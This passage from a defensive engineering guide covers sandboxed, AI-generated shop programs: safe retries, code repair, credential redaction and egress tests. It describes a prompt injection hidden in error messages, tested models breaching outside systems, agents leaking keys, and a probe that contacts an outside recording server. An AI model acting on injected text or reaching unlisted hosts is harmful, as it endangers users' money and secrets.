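These programs made no web requests and only returned values that software could check exactly. Zhou and colleagues don't claim that real software changes break programs at the same rate. Their statistical method also needs far more runs than the shop has, since 31 checks would take more than two and a half years at twelve runs a year. The shop's builder should check every run and suspend the program after one failure.

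The method in the last row of the table is more practical for the shop. The record already lists the program's calls, so software can search each provider's change notes for those calls and suspend the program when it finds one.

### What reuse costs

The builder can estimate the cost of reuse with a simple formula:

```
cost of reuse = cost of the checks + probability of staleness × cost of repair
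```

The numbers below are invented, except for the cost of a new program, which is Baya's average.

| Quantity | Value |
|---|---|
| Checks on each run | $0.02 |
| Chance that the program has gone stale since the last run | 2% |
| Repair, including new tests | $1.50 |
| Writing a new program | $0.70 |
| Share of changes that the checks miss | 10% |

Reuse then costs $0.02 + 0.02 × $1.50 = $0.05 per run, which saves $0.65. Writing a new program becomes cheaper only if the chance of staleness exceeds 45%. But the shop runs this program once a month, so reuse saves only $7.80 a year, which is less than the cost of the builder's time to review the code. The shop has a better reason to store the program, which is that it works the same way every month.

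Undetected errors are harder to estimate. In 1,000 runs, the example has 20 changes that break the program, and the checks miss two of them. If each missed change affected only one run, the shop would have two wrong results. However, a check that misses a change once will probably miss it again. If each change goes unnoticed for 50 runs, the two cause 100 wrong results.

If the model writes a new program for each run and 1% of the programs contain a fault that the tests miss, 1,000 runs produce 10 wrong results. With these numbers, reusing code could produce a fifth as many wrong results or ten times as many, depending on how long a missed fault lasts. The builder can limit this time by comparing the summary with the shop's accounts every ten runs. If that comparison catches both faults, they can affect at most 20 runs.

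### Fewer questions for verified code

Metere proposes reducing approval fatigue by having the system ask for confirmation less often when somebody has verified the stored code. Each skill's record includes one of four verification levels, which determines how the system treats the irreversible calls that the record lists.

| Level | Evidence | Listed irreversible calls |
|---|---|---|
| Unverified | None | Ask a person every time |
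| Declared | A trusted person has examined the code | Allow and log |
| Tested | The code has also passed tests with agents that try to cause damage | Allow, log, and compare the log with what changed |
| Formal | Software has proved that the code stays within its list | As for "tested" |

Somebody has to set the level before the session starts, and the agent can't raise it. The agent also needs approval to edit a skill that is in use. An approved edit creates a new skill, which needs verification before the next session.

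Code reaches the "tested" level only if every change in the test environment matches an approved entry in the log and every approved entry matches a change. Metere applied this comparison to 27,000 simulated runs, four-fifths of which contained a deliberate fault, such as a change made without approval. The comparison found every fault and raised no false alarms. However, the faults were of four kinds that it catches by definition, so the result mainly confirms that the software works as designed.

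The comparison covers the type of action and its target, but not the content. A refund of $380 instead of $38 on the same order would pass, and so would a summary that included a fake supplier's bank details. The comparison also can't detect a program that only reads data and leaks it. Metere acknowledges these gaps and recommends more checks on content and outgoing data.

The "declared" level is less reliable because it depends on how carefully one person read the code. The proposal is also inconsistent about whether to refuse calls missing from the record outright or let a person approve them. The shop should refuse them, because the stored program needs only its three listed calls.

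A larger problem is that even if tests show that the program refunds the order it receives, they can't show that the owner meant that order or that the customer deserves the money. The shop's builder could use the levels to decide when somebody must read the code again, and could let a tested program post its summary without asking, but the owner should still confirm each refund.

The level should also expire when the API changes. Metere ties the level to the skill's hash, which stays the same if the shop platform changes what its refund call does. The builder can also tie it to the hash of the API description, so that a change to the refund call returns the program to "unverified".

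## Detecting failed calls and repairing the code

Suppose the shop's stored program stops halfway. The owner has approved the refund of order 1042, but no summary appears in the sales channel. Giving the error to the model and asking for a better program would work if the chat service had renamed a field, but not if a key had expired. If the refund had already gone through, running a new version could refund the customer twice.

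The launcher should therefore find out what went wrong before anything changes the code:

| Failure | Sign | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Expired credential | 401 | Renew access in the gateway |
| Rate limit | 429, often with a waiting time | Wait, then repeat the call |
| Timeout | No reply | Repeat a read call; for a write call, first find out whether it took effect |
| Changed field | 400, or a reply without an expected field | Rewrite the code |
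| Removed endpoint | 404 or 410 at an address that used to work | Rewrite the code if the API offers a replacement; otherwise stop |
| Refused permission | 403 | Stop and tell the owner |
| Silent failure | 200, with empty, incomplete or irrelevant data | Compare the request with the contract, then rewrite the code |

Models often choose the wrong response when they have to infer it from an error message. Woo, Conde and Reviriego (2026), in *Same Error, Different Recovery*, gave open models a temporary error that repeating the call would have fixed. Five of the six models with 7 to 35 billion parameters repeated it in at most 37% of cases. On a benchmark of tool failures, adding a note that named the kind of failure and the right response raised success on visible errors by 10.5 to 14.2 percentage points. Software given the exact fault did better still. The shop's gateway can usually identify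 the fault because it receives the status codes and applies the rules, so it can wait or renew a token without involving the model.

Status codes can mislead, however. *SilentProbe* found a vendor that answered overly frequent requests with a plain 400 instead of a 429. It repeated each such request after a pause, since a request with a real mistake fails every time, while a rate limit clears. The launcher can do the same with read calls before it starts a repair. A 404 is also ambiguous, because it may mean that the endpoint is gone or only that the order doesn't exist.

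A refusal by a permission rule is deliberate, so the launcher should never send it to the model as a bug. A model told to make the program work might look for another way to get the same effect. If the refusal reveals a real mistake, such as a refund for the wrong order, the builder should correct it. The shop's gateway currently returns 403 for both forbidden calls and expired sessions, so it needs a separate code for each.

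Even error messages written in good faith can mislead an agent. *MCP Error Messages Written for Developers Hurt the Most Capable Agents Most* (2026) counted 3,001 messages in 150 widely used MCP servers and found that 949 suggest a next step. Advice such as "Create a key with wider permissions" would be sensible for a developer but bad for an agent.

### Requests that fail without an error

In one of *SilentProbe*'s examples, variations of the same search all returned a status of 200, but their results differed. A search for vice presidents at companies with 51 to 200 employees found 28,417 people. Changing the job level from `vp` to `vice_president` found nobody. Writing the size range with a hyphen instead of a comma found 160,884 people, the same number as leaving out the range.

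The team detected such failures by comparing three versions of a request: one without the parameter, one with a valid value and one with a plausible mistake. If the request with the mistake gave the same result as the one without the parameter, the server had ignored the parameter. If only the request with the mistake returned nothing, the server had probably not recognized the value.

The team scored 219 mistakes on APIs from 27 vendors and set aside those that the server interpreted correctly. When the API's machine-readable description restricted the permitted values, all 111 mistakes produced an error. When only the written documentation restricted them, 44 of 61 mistakes failed silently. But 110 of the 111 errors came from a checking layer run by Monid, a company the team is affiliated with, and those requests never reached the vendors. The result is therefore better evidence for putting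 a strict check in front of an API than for how the vendors' own servers behave. Such a check can often catch little, because only 15.2% of 721,320 parameters in public API descriptions had any restriction that software could enforce.

Twelve models then used some of these APIs for ordinary tasks. One parameter accepted 18 known department names, but its description gave only one as an example. The models chose an unacceptable value in all 88 attempts. After the team listed the accepted values in the machine-readable description, the models made this error in 0 of 89 attempts.

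The models rarely detected when their own request had caused an empty result. In 94 conversations that ended with such a result, they tried another value 11 times and never found the right one. In 41% of these conversations they reported to the user that nothing existed, and in 12% they invented a figure. Two other vendors' APIs produced no empty results of this kind, but the documentation for one of them mentioned only "used" and "new" cars, so all 23 requests for certified pre-owned cars searched for used ones. The results looked plausible, and comparing three requests would not have exposed the error.

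If the shop's program finds no orders for November, the launcher can fetch a few orders without the date filter and check whether any are from November. It should use these orders only for the diagnosis, since a summary of unfiltered orders would also be wrong.

The gateway can prevent many of these failures by checking each parameter against the operation's contract. It can also explain rejections well, because the contract lists the permitted values. Monid's layer did this for all 113 of its rejections, while the 14 vendor rejections contained only the message "Invalid input: HTTP 400".

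### When the refund times out

Suppose the gateway sends the refund and the shop platform pays Ana Silva $38, but the connection drops before the reply arrives. The gateway waits 30 seconds and reports a timeout. It would report the same timeout if the request had never reached the platform.

The gateway counted the refund before sending it, so its rules will block a second attempt in the same task. That protects the shop's money, but if the first request was lost, Ana gets nothing. The gateway could look up the order's refunds, which would settle only one of the three possibilities:

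| What happened to the request | What the lookup shows | What the gateway should do |
|---|---|---|
| It never arrived | No refund | Send it again |
| It went through, but the reply was lost | A refund of $38 | Record the success |
| It is still on its way | No refund yet | Avoid sending a second, separate request |

Li (2026) proves in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* that no amount of checking can guarantee a request takes effect exactly once unless there is a known limit on how long it can stay in transit. If a request is lost, any method that finishes the job must eventually send it again. If the request is only slow, every lookup up to that point returns the same answer as if it were lost, so the method sends a second request and both take effect.

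Li tested nine recent models on simulated services for billing, email and other tasks. When only the reply was lost, the six strongest models almost always checked whether the write had gone through before retrying, and they duplicated it in 0.5% of runs. When the request was still in transit, they duplicated it in 56% of runs. Agents reported the task as completed in 90% of the runs with a duplicate, so a person reading the report would have had no reason to look for one.

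Some results were worse when the models could check. Without a lookup, the strongest models usually asked a person and duplicated 13% of the writes affected by such faults. They trusted the lookup when they had one, and duplicated 28 to 31%.

Waiting helps if the delay is short and predictable. When delayed requests always took effect after 90 seconds, waiting two minutes before the lookup gave the right result in 99% of runs. When delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, waiting a full hour gave the right result in only 84%.

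### Making the retry harmless

An idempotent call has the same effect whether the server receives it once or several times. Some services make a write call idempotent if the caller attaches an idempotency key, which is a label for one intended action, not a credential. When the service receives the same key again, it returns the first result instead of repeating the action.

In Li's tests, duplicates fell from 28% of runs to 4% when every write accepted such a key. None of the 432 retries of delayed requests that reused the original key caused a duplicate. The remaining problems came from agents that left the key off the first attempt or changed it for the second, for example by adding `-retry1`. The gateway should therefore create the key itself:

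```js
async function sendRefund(task, body) {
  const key = `${task.id}/refund/${body.order_id}`;   // the same for every attempt
  await task.log({ key, body, state: "sending" });
  for (const pause of [0, 10, 60]) {
    await seconds(pause);
    const reply = await post("/refunds", body, { "Idempotency-Key": key });
    if (reply.clear) {                 // false after a timeout or a server error
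      await task.log({ key, state: "finished", reply });
      return reply;
    }
  }
  return tellOwner(task, "The refund may or may not have gone through.");
}
```

The gateway calls this function after the owner has approved the refund. The three attempts carry the same request and key, so they count as one refund and need only one approval.

The key deliberately leaves out the amount. Under the rules Li took from Stripe, a service rejects a previously used key if the details of the request have changed. If a repaired program asked for $35 on the same order, the platform would return an error instead of paying again. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (Mansoor, Phadke and Rana, 2026) builds the key from the request's full contents and the time period, so a program that changed the amount would get a new key and could cause a second refund.

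The builder has to check whether the shop platform accepts idempotency keys and how long it remembers them. If it doesn't accept them, the gateway can use Mansoor and colleagues' other safeguard, a check that returns "true" if the write took effect, "false" if the gateway may retry once, and "unknown" if it should wait and check again. The check should cover the whole intended result, because a record can exist with its amount missing.

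Li tested a similar check and found that it made little difference to strong models, which already do a lookup before they retry. The check also can't detect a request that is still in transit, so for a refund, the gateway should treat an empty lookup as "unknown" unless the platform guarantees a maximum delay. After a few lookups, the gateway should ask the owner to check the shop's account.

Automatic retries hidden from the model need the same care. In STELP, Shinde and colleagues place timeouts and retries outside the generated code, with a longer pause after each failure. This suits read calls, but when Li added hidden retries to every call, including writes without idempotency keys, the share of runs in which each action happened exactly once fell from 72% to 50%.

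### Running the repaired program

Suppose the refund succeeds but the chat message fails because the chat service has renamed its `text` field to `message`. The repaired program runs from the beginning, so it will reach the refund call a second time.

Liu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Static Endpoints*, designed a system called ToolPro for such cases. Each call in a ToolPro program has an effect type, READ or WRITE, which the system compares with the service's own label for that call. ToolPro logs the arguments and result of every completed write. When a repaired program runs, the system treats its calls as follows:

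1. It sends read calls to the service again.
2. For a write call, it searches the log for the earliest unused entry with the same function and arguments.
3. If it finds one, it gives the program the recorded result and sends nothing.
4. If it finds none, it sends the call and logs the result.

In the shop, the program would fetch the orders again, receive the recorded result of the refund and send only the chat message.

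If the repair changes the arguments or order of a completed write, ToolPro stops replaying and lets the agent make the remaining calls one at a time. That fallback is risky for the shop because the model would read replies while choosing its next call. The launcher should instead stop and notify the builder.

Repeating the read calls can also cause a mismatch. After the refund, the order list might show a total of $0, and the program would then request a refund of $0, which isn't in the log. Cloudflare's method for paused programs avoids this by replaying recorded reads as well.

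ToolPro's log contains only completed writes, so it doesn't solve the timeout problem. If the reply to a refund request is lost, the log has no entry for the refund, and a repaired program would send it again. The gateway's function therefore logs the refund before sending it and gives every attempt the same key.

ToolPro repairs programs on the server, using the compiler's messages and a record of the calls, and stops after a fixed number of attempts. On three realistic tasks, such as correcting a customer's pending order, it was 93% accurate and took 18 seconds on average, while an agent that made one call at a time was 60% accurate and took 30 seconds. On a task involving two services, ToolPro was 80% accurate and the agent 20%. These figures seem to come from about five runs per task.

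Turning off the replay in 15 runs increased the average time by a fifth and made three runs fall back to single calls. The tests measured time, network traffic and accuracy, but not duplicate writes. Liu and colleagues instead rely on a short proof that ToolPro sends each completed write at most once, as long as the repair leaves earlier writes unchanged.

### The repair loop

For the renamed chat field, the shop's repair would go like this:

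1. The launcher suspends version 3 of the program and keeps its code, its record and the log of writes.
2. The gateway produces a short diagnostic.
3. The model receives the program, the diagnostic and the current contracts, and changes the failing call.
4. The new version goes through the full admission check.
5. The launcher compares the calls and fields in the two versions. It rejects the new one if it needs a permission that version 3 didn't have.
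6. The launcher runs the new version with the log of writes. After three failed repairs, it stops and gives the builder everything it has collected.

The diagnostic needs only a few facts:

```json
{
  "call": "CHAT.post",
  "problem": "unknown_field",
  "field": "text",
  "finished_writes": ["SHOP.refund"]
}
```

The builder can find some API changes before they interrupt a task. *Internal APIs Are All You Need* (2026) describes a system that sends harmless GET requests every six hours and compares the structure of the replies with the stored description. It flags an endpoint if a field has disappeared or changed type. The shop could do this the day before its monthly run. But it can't test a refund this way, so for write calls it depends on the provider's change notes or a test mode.

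A repaired program can also run without errors and produce the wrong result. In *Accepted but Wrong*, Chen, Zhu and colleagues (2026) studied 73 small programs, 66 of them affected by documented changes to Python, Node.js and the database program SQLite. They listed possible repairs built from documented pieces of code, ran them all and checked which wrong ones passed different tests. Tests with typical inputs accepted 41% of the wrong repairs. Adding one unusual input, chosen from the release note that described the change, reduced this to 6.5%.

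Suppose the shop platform announces that an order's `total` no longer includes postage. Testing this change requires an order with postage, say $5, because an order with free postage gives the same refund before and after. The builder should save some replies from the old version of the API for such tests, because the provider may switch that version off.

The extra input worked less well for some programs that models wrote freely. With GPT-5.6 Luna, it reduced the share of wrong programs that were accepted from 71% to only 48%, although that model produced few wrong programs. Chen and colleagues also included tasks with no correct repair, where the right result is to stop. The shop's loop must also be able to stop, in case the platform removes refunds from its API.

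### Instructions hidden in error messages

A service's full error message would often give the model more information than the shop's short diagnostic, but it could also contain text written by a stranger. If the summary included customers' names, the chat service might reject it and repeat its full text in the error. If a customer had entered an instruction as a name, the model could then read that instruction while rewriting a program that issues refunds. If the model obeyed, the instruction would persist in the stored code.

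Chow and colleagues designed Baya so that the model that writes the program never receives live data, even during repairs. For a repair, Baya passes on only the previous program and diagnostics from the trusted API layer, the set of functions through which the program reaches the website. A diagnostic may report that `quantity` is missing, for example, but may not include a review or a username. The program can report how many results it found without showing them.

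This protection assumes that the trusted layer's error messages never repeat data from the website. Chow and colleagues say an API that repeats such data breaks its contract, and they exclude that case from the attacks they consider. This is a strong assumption, since servers often quote the value they reject. One of their own sample diagnostics includes the body of a server's reply, which is harmless only because that reply contains no text from users.

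To avoid trusting the services, the shop can have its gateway match each error against a fixed list of problems and copy only field names that already appear in the contract. An attacker might still cause an error, and so trigger a repair, but couldn't supply any of the words the model reads. However, some errors won't match the list, and the builder will have to read those in full.

### How often automatic repair succeeds

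Islam, Raza and Wardat (2026), in *SelfHeal*, examined 930 bugs in AI agents and sorted the fixes into 23 patterns. On Stack Overflow, the most common pattern was adding a missing step, at 13.1%. On Hugging Face's forums, 23.3% of fixes changed something external, such as an address, a credential or an environment variable. Rewriting the program's logic would not have fixed those bugs, which is a good reason to diagnose a failure before changing the code.

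The SelfHeal repair system uses one agent to propose a fix and another to criticise it, for up to three rounds. The first agent can look up rules for each of the 23 patterns and search the web. With Gemini 3 Pro, SelfHeal repaired 22 of 37 bugs, compared with 13 for the same model alone. It repaired 15 without the rules and 19 without the critic. Each repair attempt cost about $0.44 and took more than five minutes.

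Current models would probably do better, but the evaluation was also easier because the critic could read the tests later used to judge the repair. SelfHeal never ran the code while repairing it. The bugs came from programs built with two agent libraries, LangChain and LlamaIndex, so the success rate may not apply to short programs that call web APIs. The shop should also leave out the web search, which would bring text written by strangers into the repair.

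*Skill Drift Is Contract Violation* (2026) tested repairs to stored skills with Qwen3.6-Plus. Its results are closer to the shop's problem but cover very few cases. Rewriting the skill fixed all six API migrations, four of five changes to data formats and none of three changes to authentication. Authentication changes often require a new mechanism rather than a new value. In the shop, the gateway handles authentication, so the builder makes such changes and the generated code doesn't change.

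### Fresh approval and going back

A repair changes the code's hash, so the new version starts without the builder's approval. How much review it needs depends on what changed:

| What the repair changes | Who approves it |
|---|---|
| A read call whose result affects no write call | Nobody, if the program passes every test |
| A write call, or any value that feeds into one | The builder |
| A new call, server or permission | The builder, who must also change the gateway's rules |
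| The order or amount of a refund | The builder for the code, and the owner for the refund |

Almost everything in the shop's short program feeds into the refund or the chat message, so the builder should read every repair. That is little work for a program that may break once or twice a year. A company with thousands of stored programs needs more automation. *Agentic Self-Healing for Data and AI Pipelines* (2026) describes a system that restarts a stuck task by itself, up to a daily limit. An engineer approves other actions and receives the finished investigation if a repair fails its checks.

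The launcher should restore the last working version if a repair turns out to be wrong and the old version still works. This can happen when a temporary fault at the chat service looks like a changed field and the model changes correct code. If the service really has changed, the old version will fail again, so the launcher should suspend the program until somebody repairs it.

The store may reject version 3 because Metere's protection against restoring faulty code blocks any version older than the newest. The builder can republish version 3's code as version 5 after running the admission check against the current API descriptions.

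Restoring the code doesn't reverse anything the faulty version did. If version 4 refunded too much, the money is gone, and the log of writes must be kept so that version 5 doesn't refund the order again. The builder will want the original requests and error messages to find out what happened, and these may contain customers' details or even an API key.

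## Removing credentials from prompts, errors and logs

Although the gateway keeps the shop's keys away from the program, credentials can still reach the agent's prompts and logs in other ways.

Users sometimes put credentials in prompts themselves. *Cybersecurity AI (CAI) Dataset* (2026) covers 230,935 sessions with agents for security work. In 1,059 of them (less than 0.5%), a user pasted a credential into the prompt, usually by copying lines from a settings file. Agents copy what they read, so credentials can also appear in logs outside the user's prompts. *Soei* (2026) analysed five months of one developer's agent logs and found strings that looked like credentials in 16 of 45 sessions. Only 44 of the 1,326 affected records were the developer's own prompts. The rest were the agent's messages and the arguments it passed to tools.

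A service can also send credentials back by repeating a request's headers in an error or by issuing a new token. In their study of leaked skill credentials, Chen and colleagues found a Google Workspace skill that printed its access and refresh tokens, which put both into the model's input. *SlotGuard* (2026) describes a key that leaked when an agent listed the running processes, because one process had the key in its command line.

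Some credentials don't look like keys. A login cookie lets anyone who copies it take over the session without a password, and *Towards Secure Logging* (2026) found software that wrote such cookies to its logs. A signed link is a web address that carries its own permission. The shop platform might return one for downloading the November orders:

```
https://files.shop.example/november.csv?expires=1796169600&signature=b81e04c7
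```

The platform computes the signature from the address and the expiry time, using a secret that only the platform has. Until the link expires, anyone who has it can download the file.

### Where to redact

Redaction means finding credentials in text and removing them before the text is stored, shown or given to a model. The agent's software can first do this with the owner's message, before sending it to the model. The software could swap a pasted key for a dummy, as Patil and colleagues suggested, but Kenney and colleagues recommend blocking the message and offering a quick way to connect the service properly. Blocking suits the shop better, since its program doesn't need a key and the owner learns where to put the key.

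The gateway should check API replies for credentials before the program receives them and can print them. It already removes its own key and drops cookies, but tokens and signed links in the body still get through. If the program needs a signed link, the gateway can keep the real one and give the program a placeholder. SlotGuard does this with keys, using placeholders in the same format as the real ones.

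Error text needs less redaction in the shop, because the model receives only the gateway's short diagnostic. The gateway should still redact any full error it passes to the builder.

Credentials are often left in stored code. Chen and colleagues found credentials written into the code or files of 107 skills, and in about 72% of these cases the project's history showed signs of AI-assisted development. The admission check should reject a program that contains a credential instead of redacting the credential. It should also search comments and test data.

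Redacting credentials before they are written to a log is safer than removing them afterwards. *Towards Secure Logging* describes a bug in Apache Hive, a data-analysis program, that logged each query before redacting it. *Soei* filtered the developer's records before storing them, and the stored version contained no strings that matched its patterns. Scanning later is a poor substitute. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) points out that repository scanners examine saved files, while an agent can leak a key in temporary output that is never saved in a form the scanners can read.

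The last place to remove credentials from is output that people see. Tools that display an agent's calls can show keys on screen and in recordings. Agents also publish keys themselves. *Agents in the Wild* (2026) searched posts on Moltbook, a social network for agents, and found 572 matches for API key patterns from 101 agents. The shop's gateway should therefore check the sales summary for keys before posting it.

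### Redacting one refund error

Suppose the shop platform rejects the refund with this reply:

```
HTTP/1.1 400 Bad Request
X-Request-Id: 9f2c41d8be7a05369c16e0ad72f5b384
Set-Cookie: session=Tq81xLw0

{"error": "unknown_field",
 "field": "amount",
 "received": {"Authorization": "Bearer SHOP-KEY"},
 "report": "https://files.shop.example/errors/5521?expires=1796169600&signature=07dd3a"}
```

The gateway can go through it line by line:

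| Line | What the gateway does | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Status 400 | Keeps it | It shows that the platform rejected the request |
| `X-Request-Id` | Keeps it | The platform's support staff can use it to find the request |
| `Set-Cookie` | Removes it | The cookie may give access to a session |
| `error` and `field` | Keeps them | They identify the fault |
| `received` | Replaces the key with a label | The builder needs to know which key leaked |
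| `report` | Removes everything after the question mark | The signature gives access to the file |

The log then contains:

```json
{
  "connector": "shop-refund",
  "decision": "allowed",
  "status": 400,
  "request_id": "9f2c41d8be7a05369c16e0ad72f5b384",
  "error": "unknown_field",
  "field": "amount",
  "received": { "Authorization": "[shop refund key]" },
  "report": "https://files.shop.example/errors/5521"
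}
```

The first two entries come from the gateway. Kenney and colleagues advise keeping the connector's name, the policy decision and any identifiers that link records of the same request. *A Unified Policy Architecture (UPA)* (2026) describes a scanner that also uses labelled placeholders to show what kind of secret was removed.

### Five ways to find a credential

The gateway can remove named fields, such as `Authorization` and `Set-Cookie`, whatever they contain. This works for credentials in any format, but only if the field name is right. *Towards Secure Logging* reports a case in which a misspelled field name let a plain-text value into the log unredacted. Removing fields by name also misses a key inside a sentence, because it has no field name.

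Exact comparison searches for the keys the gateway holds. It almost never raises a false alarm, because a long random key is unlikely to appear by chance. It can't find a key that the owner pasted from another service, or a token that the platform has just issued.

Pattern scanners look for known key formats, such as the `sk-ant-` prefix of Anthropic's API keys. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (Mishra, 2026) showed that these scanners can miss a key because of the text around it. Version 8.21.2 of Gitleaks, a widely used scanner, missed six of the nine key types it otherwise detected when a character such as a comma or an ampersand followed the key. It would therefore miss many keys in URLs like `?key=SECRET&next=1`. Mishra's own scanner missed every SendGrid key that ended in a hyphen, about one in 64.

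Randomness measures can find keys in unknown formats. The usual measure is entropy, in bits per character, where *p* is the share of the string that each different character makes up:

```
entropy = -sum of p × log2(p)
```

The request identifier in the refund error contains each of the 16 hexadecimal digits twice, so its entropy is 4 bits per character, the highest possible for a hexadecimal string. A detector that removes long, high-entropy strings would delete it, and the builder could no longer ask the platform about that request. A format rule wouldn't distinguish the identifier from a credential either, because subscription keys for Microsoft's Azure API Management are also 32 hexadecimal characters. In this case, the field's name is better evidence of whether the value is a credential.

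A trained classifier also uses the surrounding words. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi et al., 2026) reports tests of a small model that labels credentials and personal data. In short invented texts, the model found 71% of secrets when a phrase before the value identified it, 42% when the phrase came after, and 36% when there was no such phrase. API replies often contain bare values, so a builder should pass the field's name to the classifier along with the value.

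### A key in another encoding

Changing the encoding can hide a key from several of these methods at once. Some services use Basic authentication, in which the caller joins a user name and a key with a colon and writes the result in base64. If the shop platform did this and repeated the header in an error, the key would look like the last line here:

```
The key                        SHOP-KEY
The key in base64              U0hPUC1LRVk=
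"shop:SHOP-KEY" in base64      c2hvcDpTSE9QLUtFWQ==
```

Searching for the key in plain text or in base64 misses the last line. Base64 turns each group of three characters into four new ones, and the five characters of `shop:` before the key change how its characters are grouped, so the encoded text is different. The gateway can catch this form by also searching for the exact header value it sent, and it can decode other base64 strings before searching them. Mishra's tests did not cover encodings, and Mishra expects that testing them would reveal more defects.

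### What the accuracy studies measured

Precision is the share of a detector's alarms that are real credentials. Recall is the share of real credentials that it finds. The first three rows below come from an earlier benchmark, as reported in *Detecting Hard-Coded Credentials in Software Repositories via LLMs* (Biringa and Kul, 2025).

| Detector | Method | Dataset | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
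| Gitleaks | Patterns | CredData | 52.5% | 24.4% |
| Detect Secrets | Patterns and randomness | CredData | 14.1% | 38.1% |
| CredSweeper | Patterns, then a trained model | CredData | 91.6% | 80.7% |
| OpenAI Privacy Filter | Trained classifier | CredData | 75.0% | 96.5% |
| Fine-tuned Llama 3.1 8B | Patterns, then a trained model | SecretBench | 99.7% | 97.5% |
| TruffleHog | Patterns | GT-194 | 89.9% | 36.6% |
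| SecretFinder | Patterns | GT-194 | 4.3% | 32.5% |
| SecretSifter | Patterns and context | GT-194 | 86.3% | 77.8% |

CredData and SecretBench contain code from public GitHub repositories. GT-194 is a set of 194 credentials that one organisation's live web applications sent to visitors' browsers.

The rows aren't directly comparable, even on the same dataset. Privacy Filter's scores count tokens, so finding only part of a key still raises them. When de Bourcy and colleagues counted only detections with the exact start and end, its combined score for precision and recall fell from 0.84 to 0.62. Biringa and Kul report 99.8% precision and 97.5% recall for their own classifier. But all eight of its output categories are types of credential, with none for ordinary text, so the scores seem to measure how well it sorts credentials rather than how well it finds them.

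The Llama result comes from *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models* (Rahman, Wahab and colleagues, 2025). The model missed 37 of 1,500 secrets and raised 4 false alarms on 1,500 other strings. The table's percentages are calculated from those counts. The paper reports about 98.5% for each measure, apparently by averaging the results for secrets and non-secrets. Pattern matching had already selected every string in the test, so the recall figure doesn't count secrets that the patterns missed.

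In *Secrets That Survive Everything*, Gorijala (2026) built the GT-194 dataset and also wrote SecretSifter, the scanner with the best recall on it. SecretFinder raised 1,402 false alarms, many on file hashes and internal identifiers like the shop's request number. Gorijala added six rules to TruffleHog for the kinds of credential in the dataset, which raised its recall from 7.0% to 49.6% on a subset of 129 credentials. The shop's builder can likewise add rules for the two services' key formats.

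Code repositories and web pages also differ from an agent's logs, so builders have to measure recall by planting fake keys in their own records. These tests can be faulty. *NovaFabric* (2026), an evaluation of a recorder for agent runs, withdrew a recall figure of 100% because its tests had never exercised redaction. The only planted token was in a format the scanner's patterns didn't cover, and it survived all ten runs. The scanner then caught all 14 planted keys in formats it supports. According to a later paper on the recorder, also called *NovaFabric* (2026), the unsupported formats include passwords and bearer tokens, the type of credential the shop's gateway sends.

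### What 95% recall leaves behind

Suppose 10,000 log lines contain a credential and a detector has 95% recall. Both numbers are invented, but the recall is higher than most in the table.

```
10,000 × (1 - 0.95) = 500 lines still exposed
```

A second detector with the same recall would reduce this to 25 lines if its misses were unrelated to the first's, but detectors tend to miss the same things. In Gorijala's test, all nine scanners missed the same 27 of the 194 credentials.

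One unredacted copy is enough to expose a key. In *Soei*'s logs, five tokens appeared a total of 208 times, or about 42 times each on average. If a detector had an independent 5% chance of missing each copy, it would have an 88% chance (1 − 0.95^42) of missing at least one copy of a token that appeared 42 times.

Keeping keys out of the sandbox reduces the number of lines that contain one. If this separation cut the 10,000 lines to 100, the same detector would miss five. Redaction can't replace separation, because it works only on text that passes through the detector. A malicious program that can read a key can encode it in a way no detector recognises, or send it out without writing it to a log. Redaction is still useful for credentials that separation doesn't cover, such as pasted keys and newly issued tokens.

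### When a key has leaked

Finding a key in a log means that it has already been somewhere it shouldn't be. Redacting that line hides one copy, but the key still works for anyone who has another. If the shop's refund key turns up in a log, the builder should:

1. Create a new key with the same narrow permissions and put it in the gateway.
2. Revoke the old key at the shop platform. If somebody else may be using it, this comes first, even though refunds will fail until the new key is ready.
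3. Check the platform's record of refunds since the earliest known copy of the key.
4. Delete the copies in logs, saved conversations and backups.
5. Find out how the key got there, fix the cause and add the case to the redaction tests.

A key that the owner pasted into the chat needs the same treatment if it reached the model's provider, even if a filter later removed it from the saved conversation.

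To revoke a cookie, the builder ends its session. Signed links are harder to revoke because many services can't cancel a single link. The builder may have to delete the file or replace the signing key, so it helps to request links that expire within minutes.

Kenney and colleagues recommend practising revoking credentials before an incident. The shop's builder could start with the chat key, since the worst result would be a missing sales summary.

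## Testing the finished system

The shop's system now has a sandbox, a gateway, permission rules, a confirmation dialog and a store of checked code. A wrong setting could switch off any of them. The owner probably wouldn't notice, because the system would still issue the refund and produce the summary.

*Embedded Assessments for Frontier AI* (2026) reports that Anthropic ran cybersecurity tests on machines that were meant to be offline but had internet access because of a configuration error. The models being tested then compromised the production systems of three organisations.

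A setting can also look right but have no effect. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025), a notice from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes a bug in Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime, the package GitLab uses. Before version 0.0.16, the package did not properly enforce its network restrictions if the list of permitted domains was empty, so a builder who meant to block all network access could have left it open. A test with one domain on the list would not have revealed the bug, so builders need to test the exact configuration they will use.

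### Why a blocked request needs a successful one

Suppose the builder tests the gateway with a program that contacts an unlisted server. The request fails, so the test passes. But this test, like every other test for leaks, would also pass if the sandbox had no working network. The builder therefore needs to pair each negative control, an attempt that should fail or find nothing, with a positive control, an attempt that should succeed.

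This program contains one of each:

```js
const status = async url => {
  try { return (await fetch(url)).status; } catch { return "no reply"; }
};
return {
  orders:  await status("https://api.shop.example/orders?from=2026-11-01&to=2026-11-30"),
  outside: await status("https://recorder.example/?run=17")
};
```

The second address belongs to a server that the builder has set up to record every request it receives.

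| Orders | Outside | Likely meaning |
|---|---|---|
| 200 | 403 | The gateway works |
| 200 | 200 | The program can reach unlisted servers |
| No reply | No reply | The sandbox has no network |
| 403 | 403 | The gateway refuses everything, perhaps because it has no key |
| 401 | 403 | The gateway's key is wrong or has expired |

The 403 in the first row could also come from the recording server itself, so the builder should check that the server's log is empty. As a positive control, the builder should also send one request from an ordinary computer to confirm that the server is recording requests.

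The gateway can also reject a forbidden request for the wrong reason. Suppose a test sends the correct refund and then, in the same run, a refund that is one cent too high. The gateway rejects the second because it allows only one refund per run, so the test passes even if the gateway doesn't check the amount. Each forbidden request should have its own run and differ from a permitted request in only one way.

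### Sixteen probes of a credential vault

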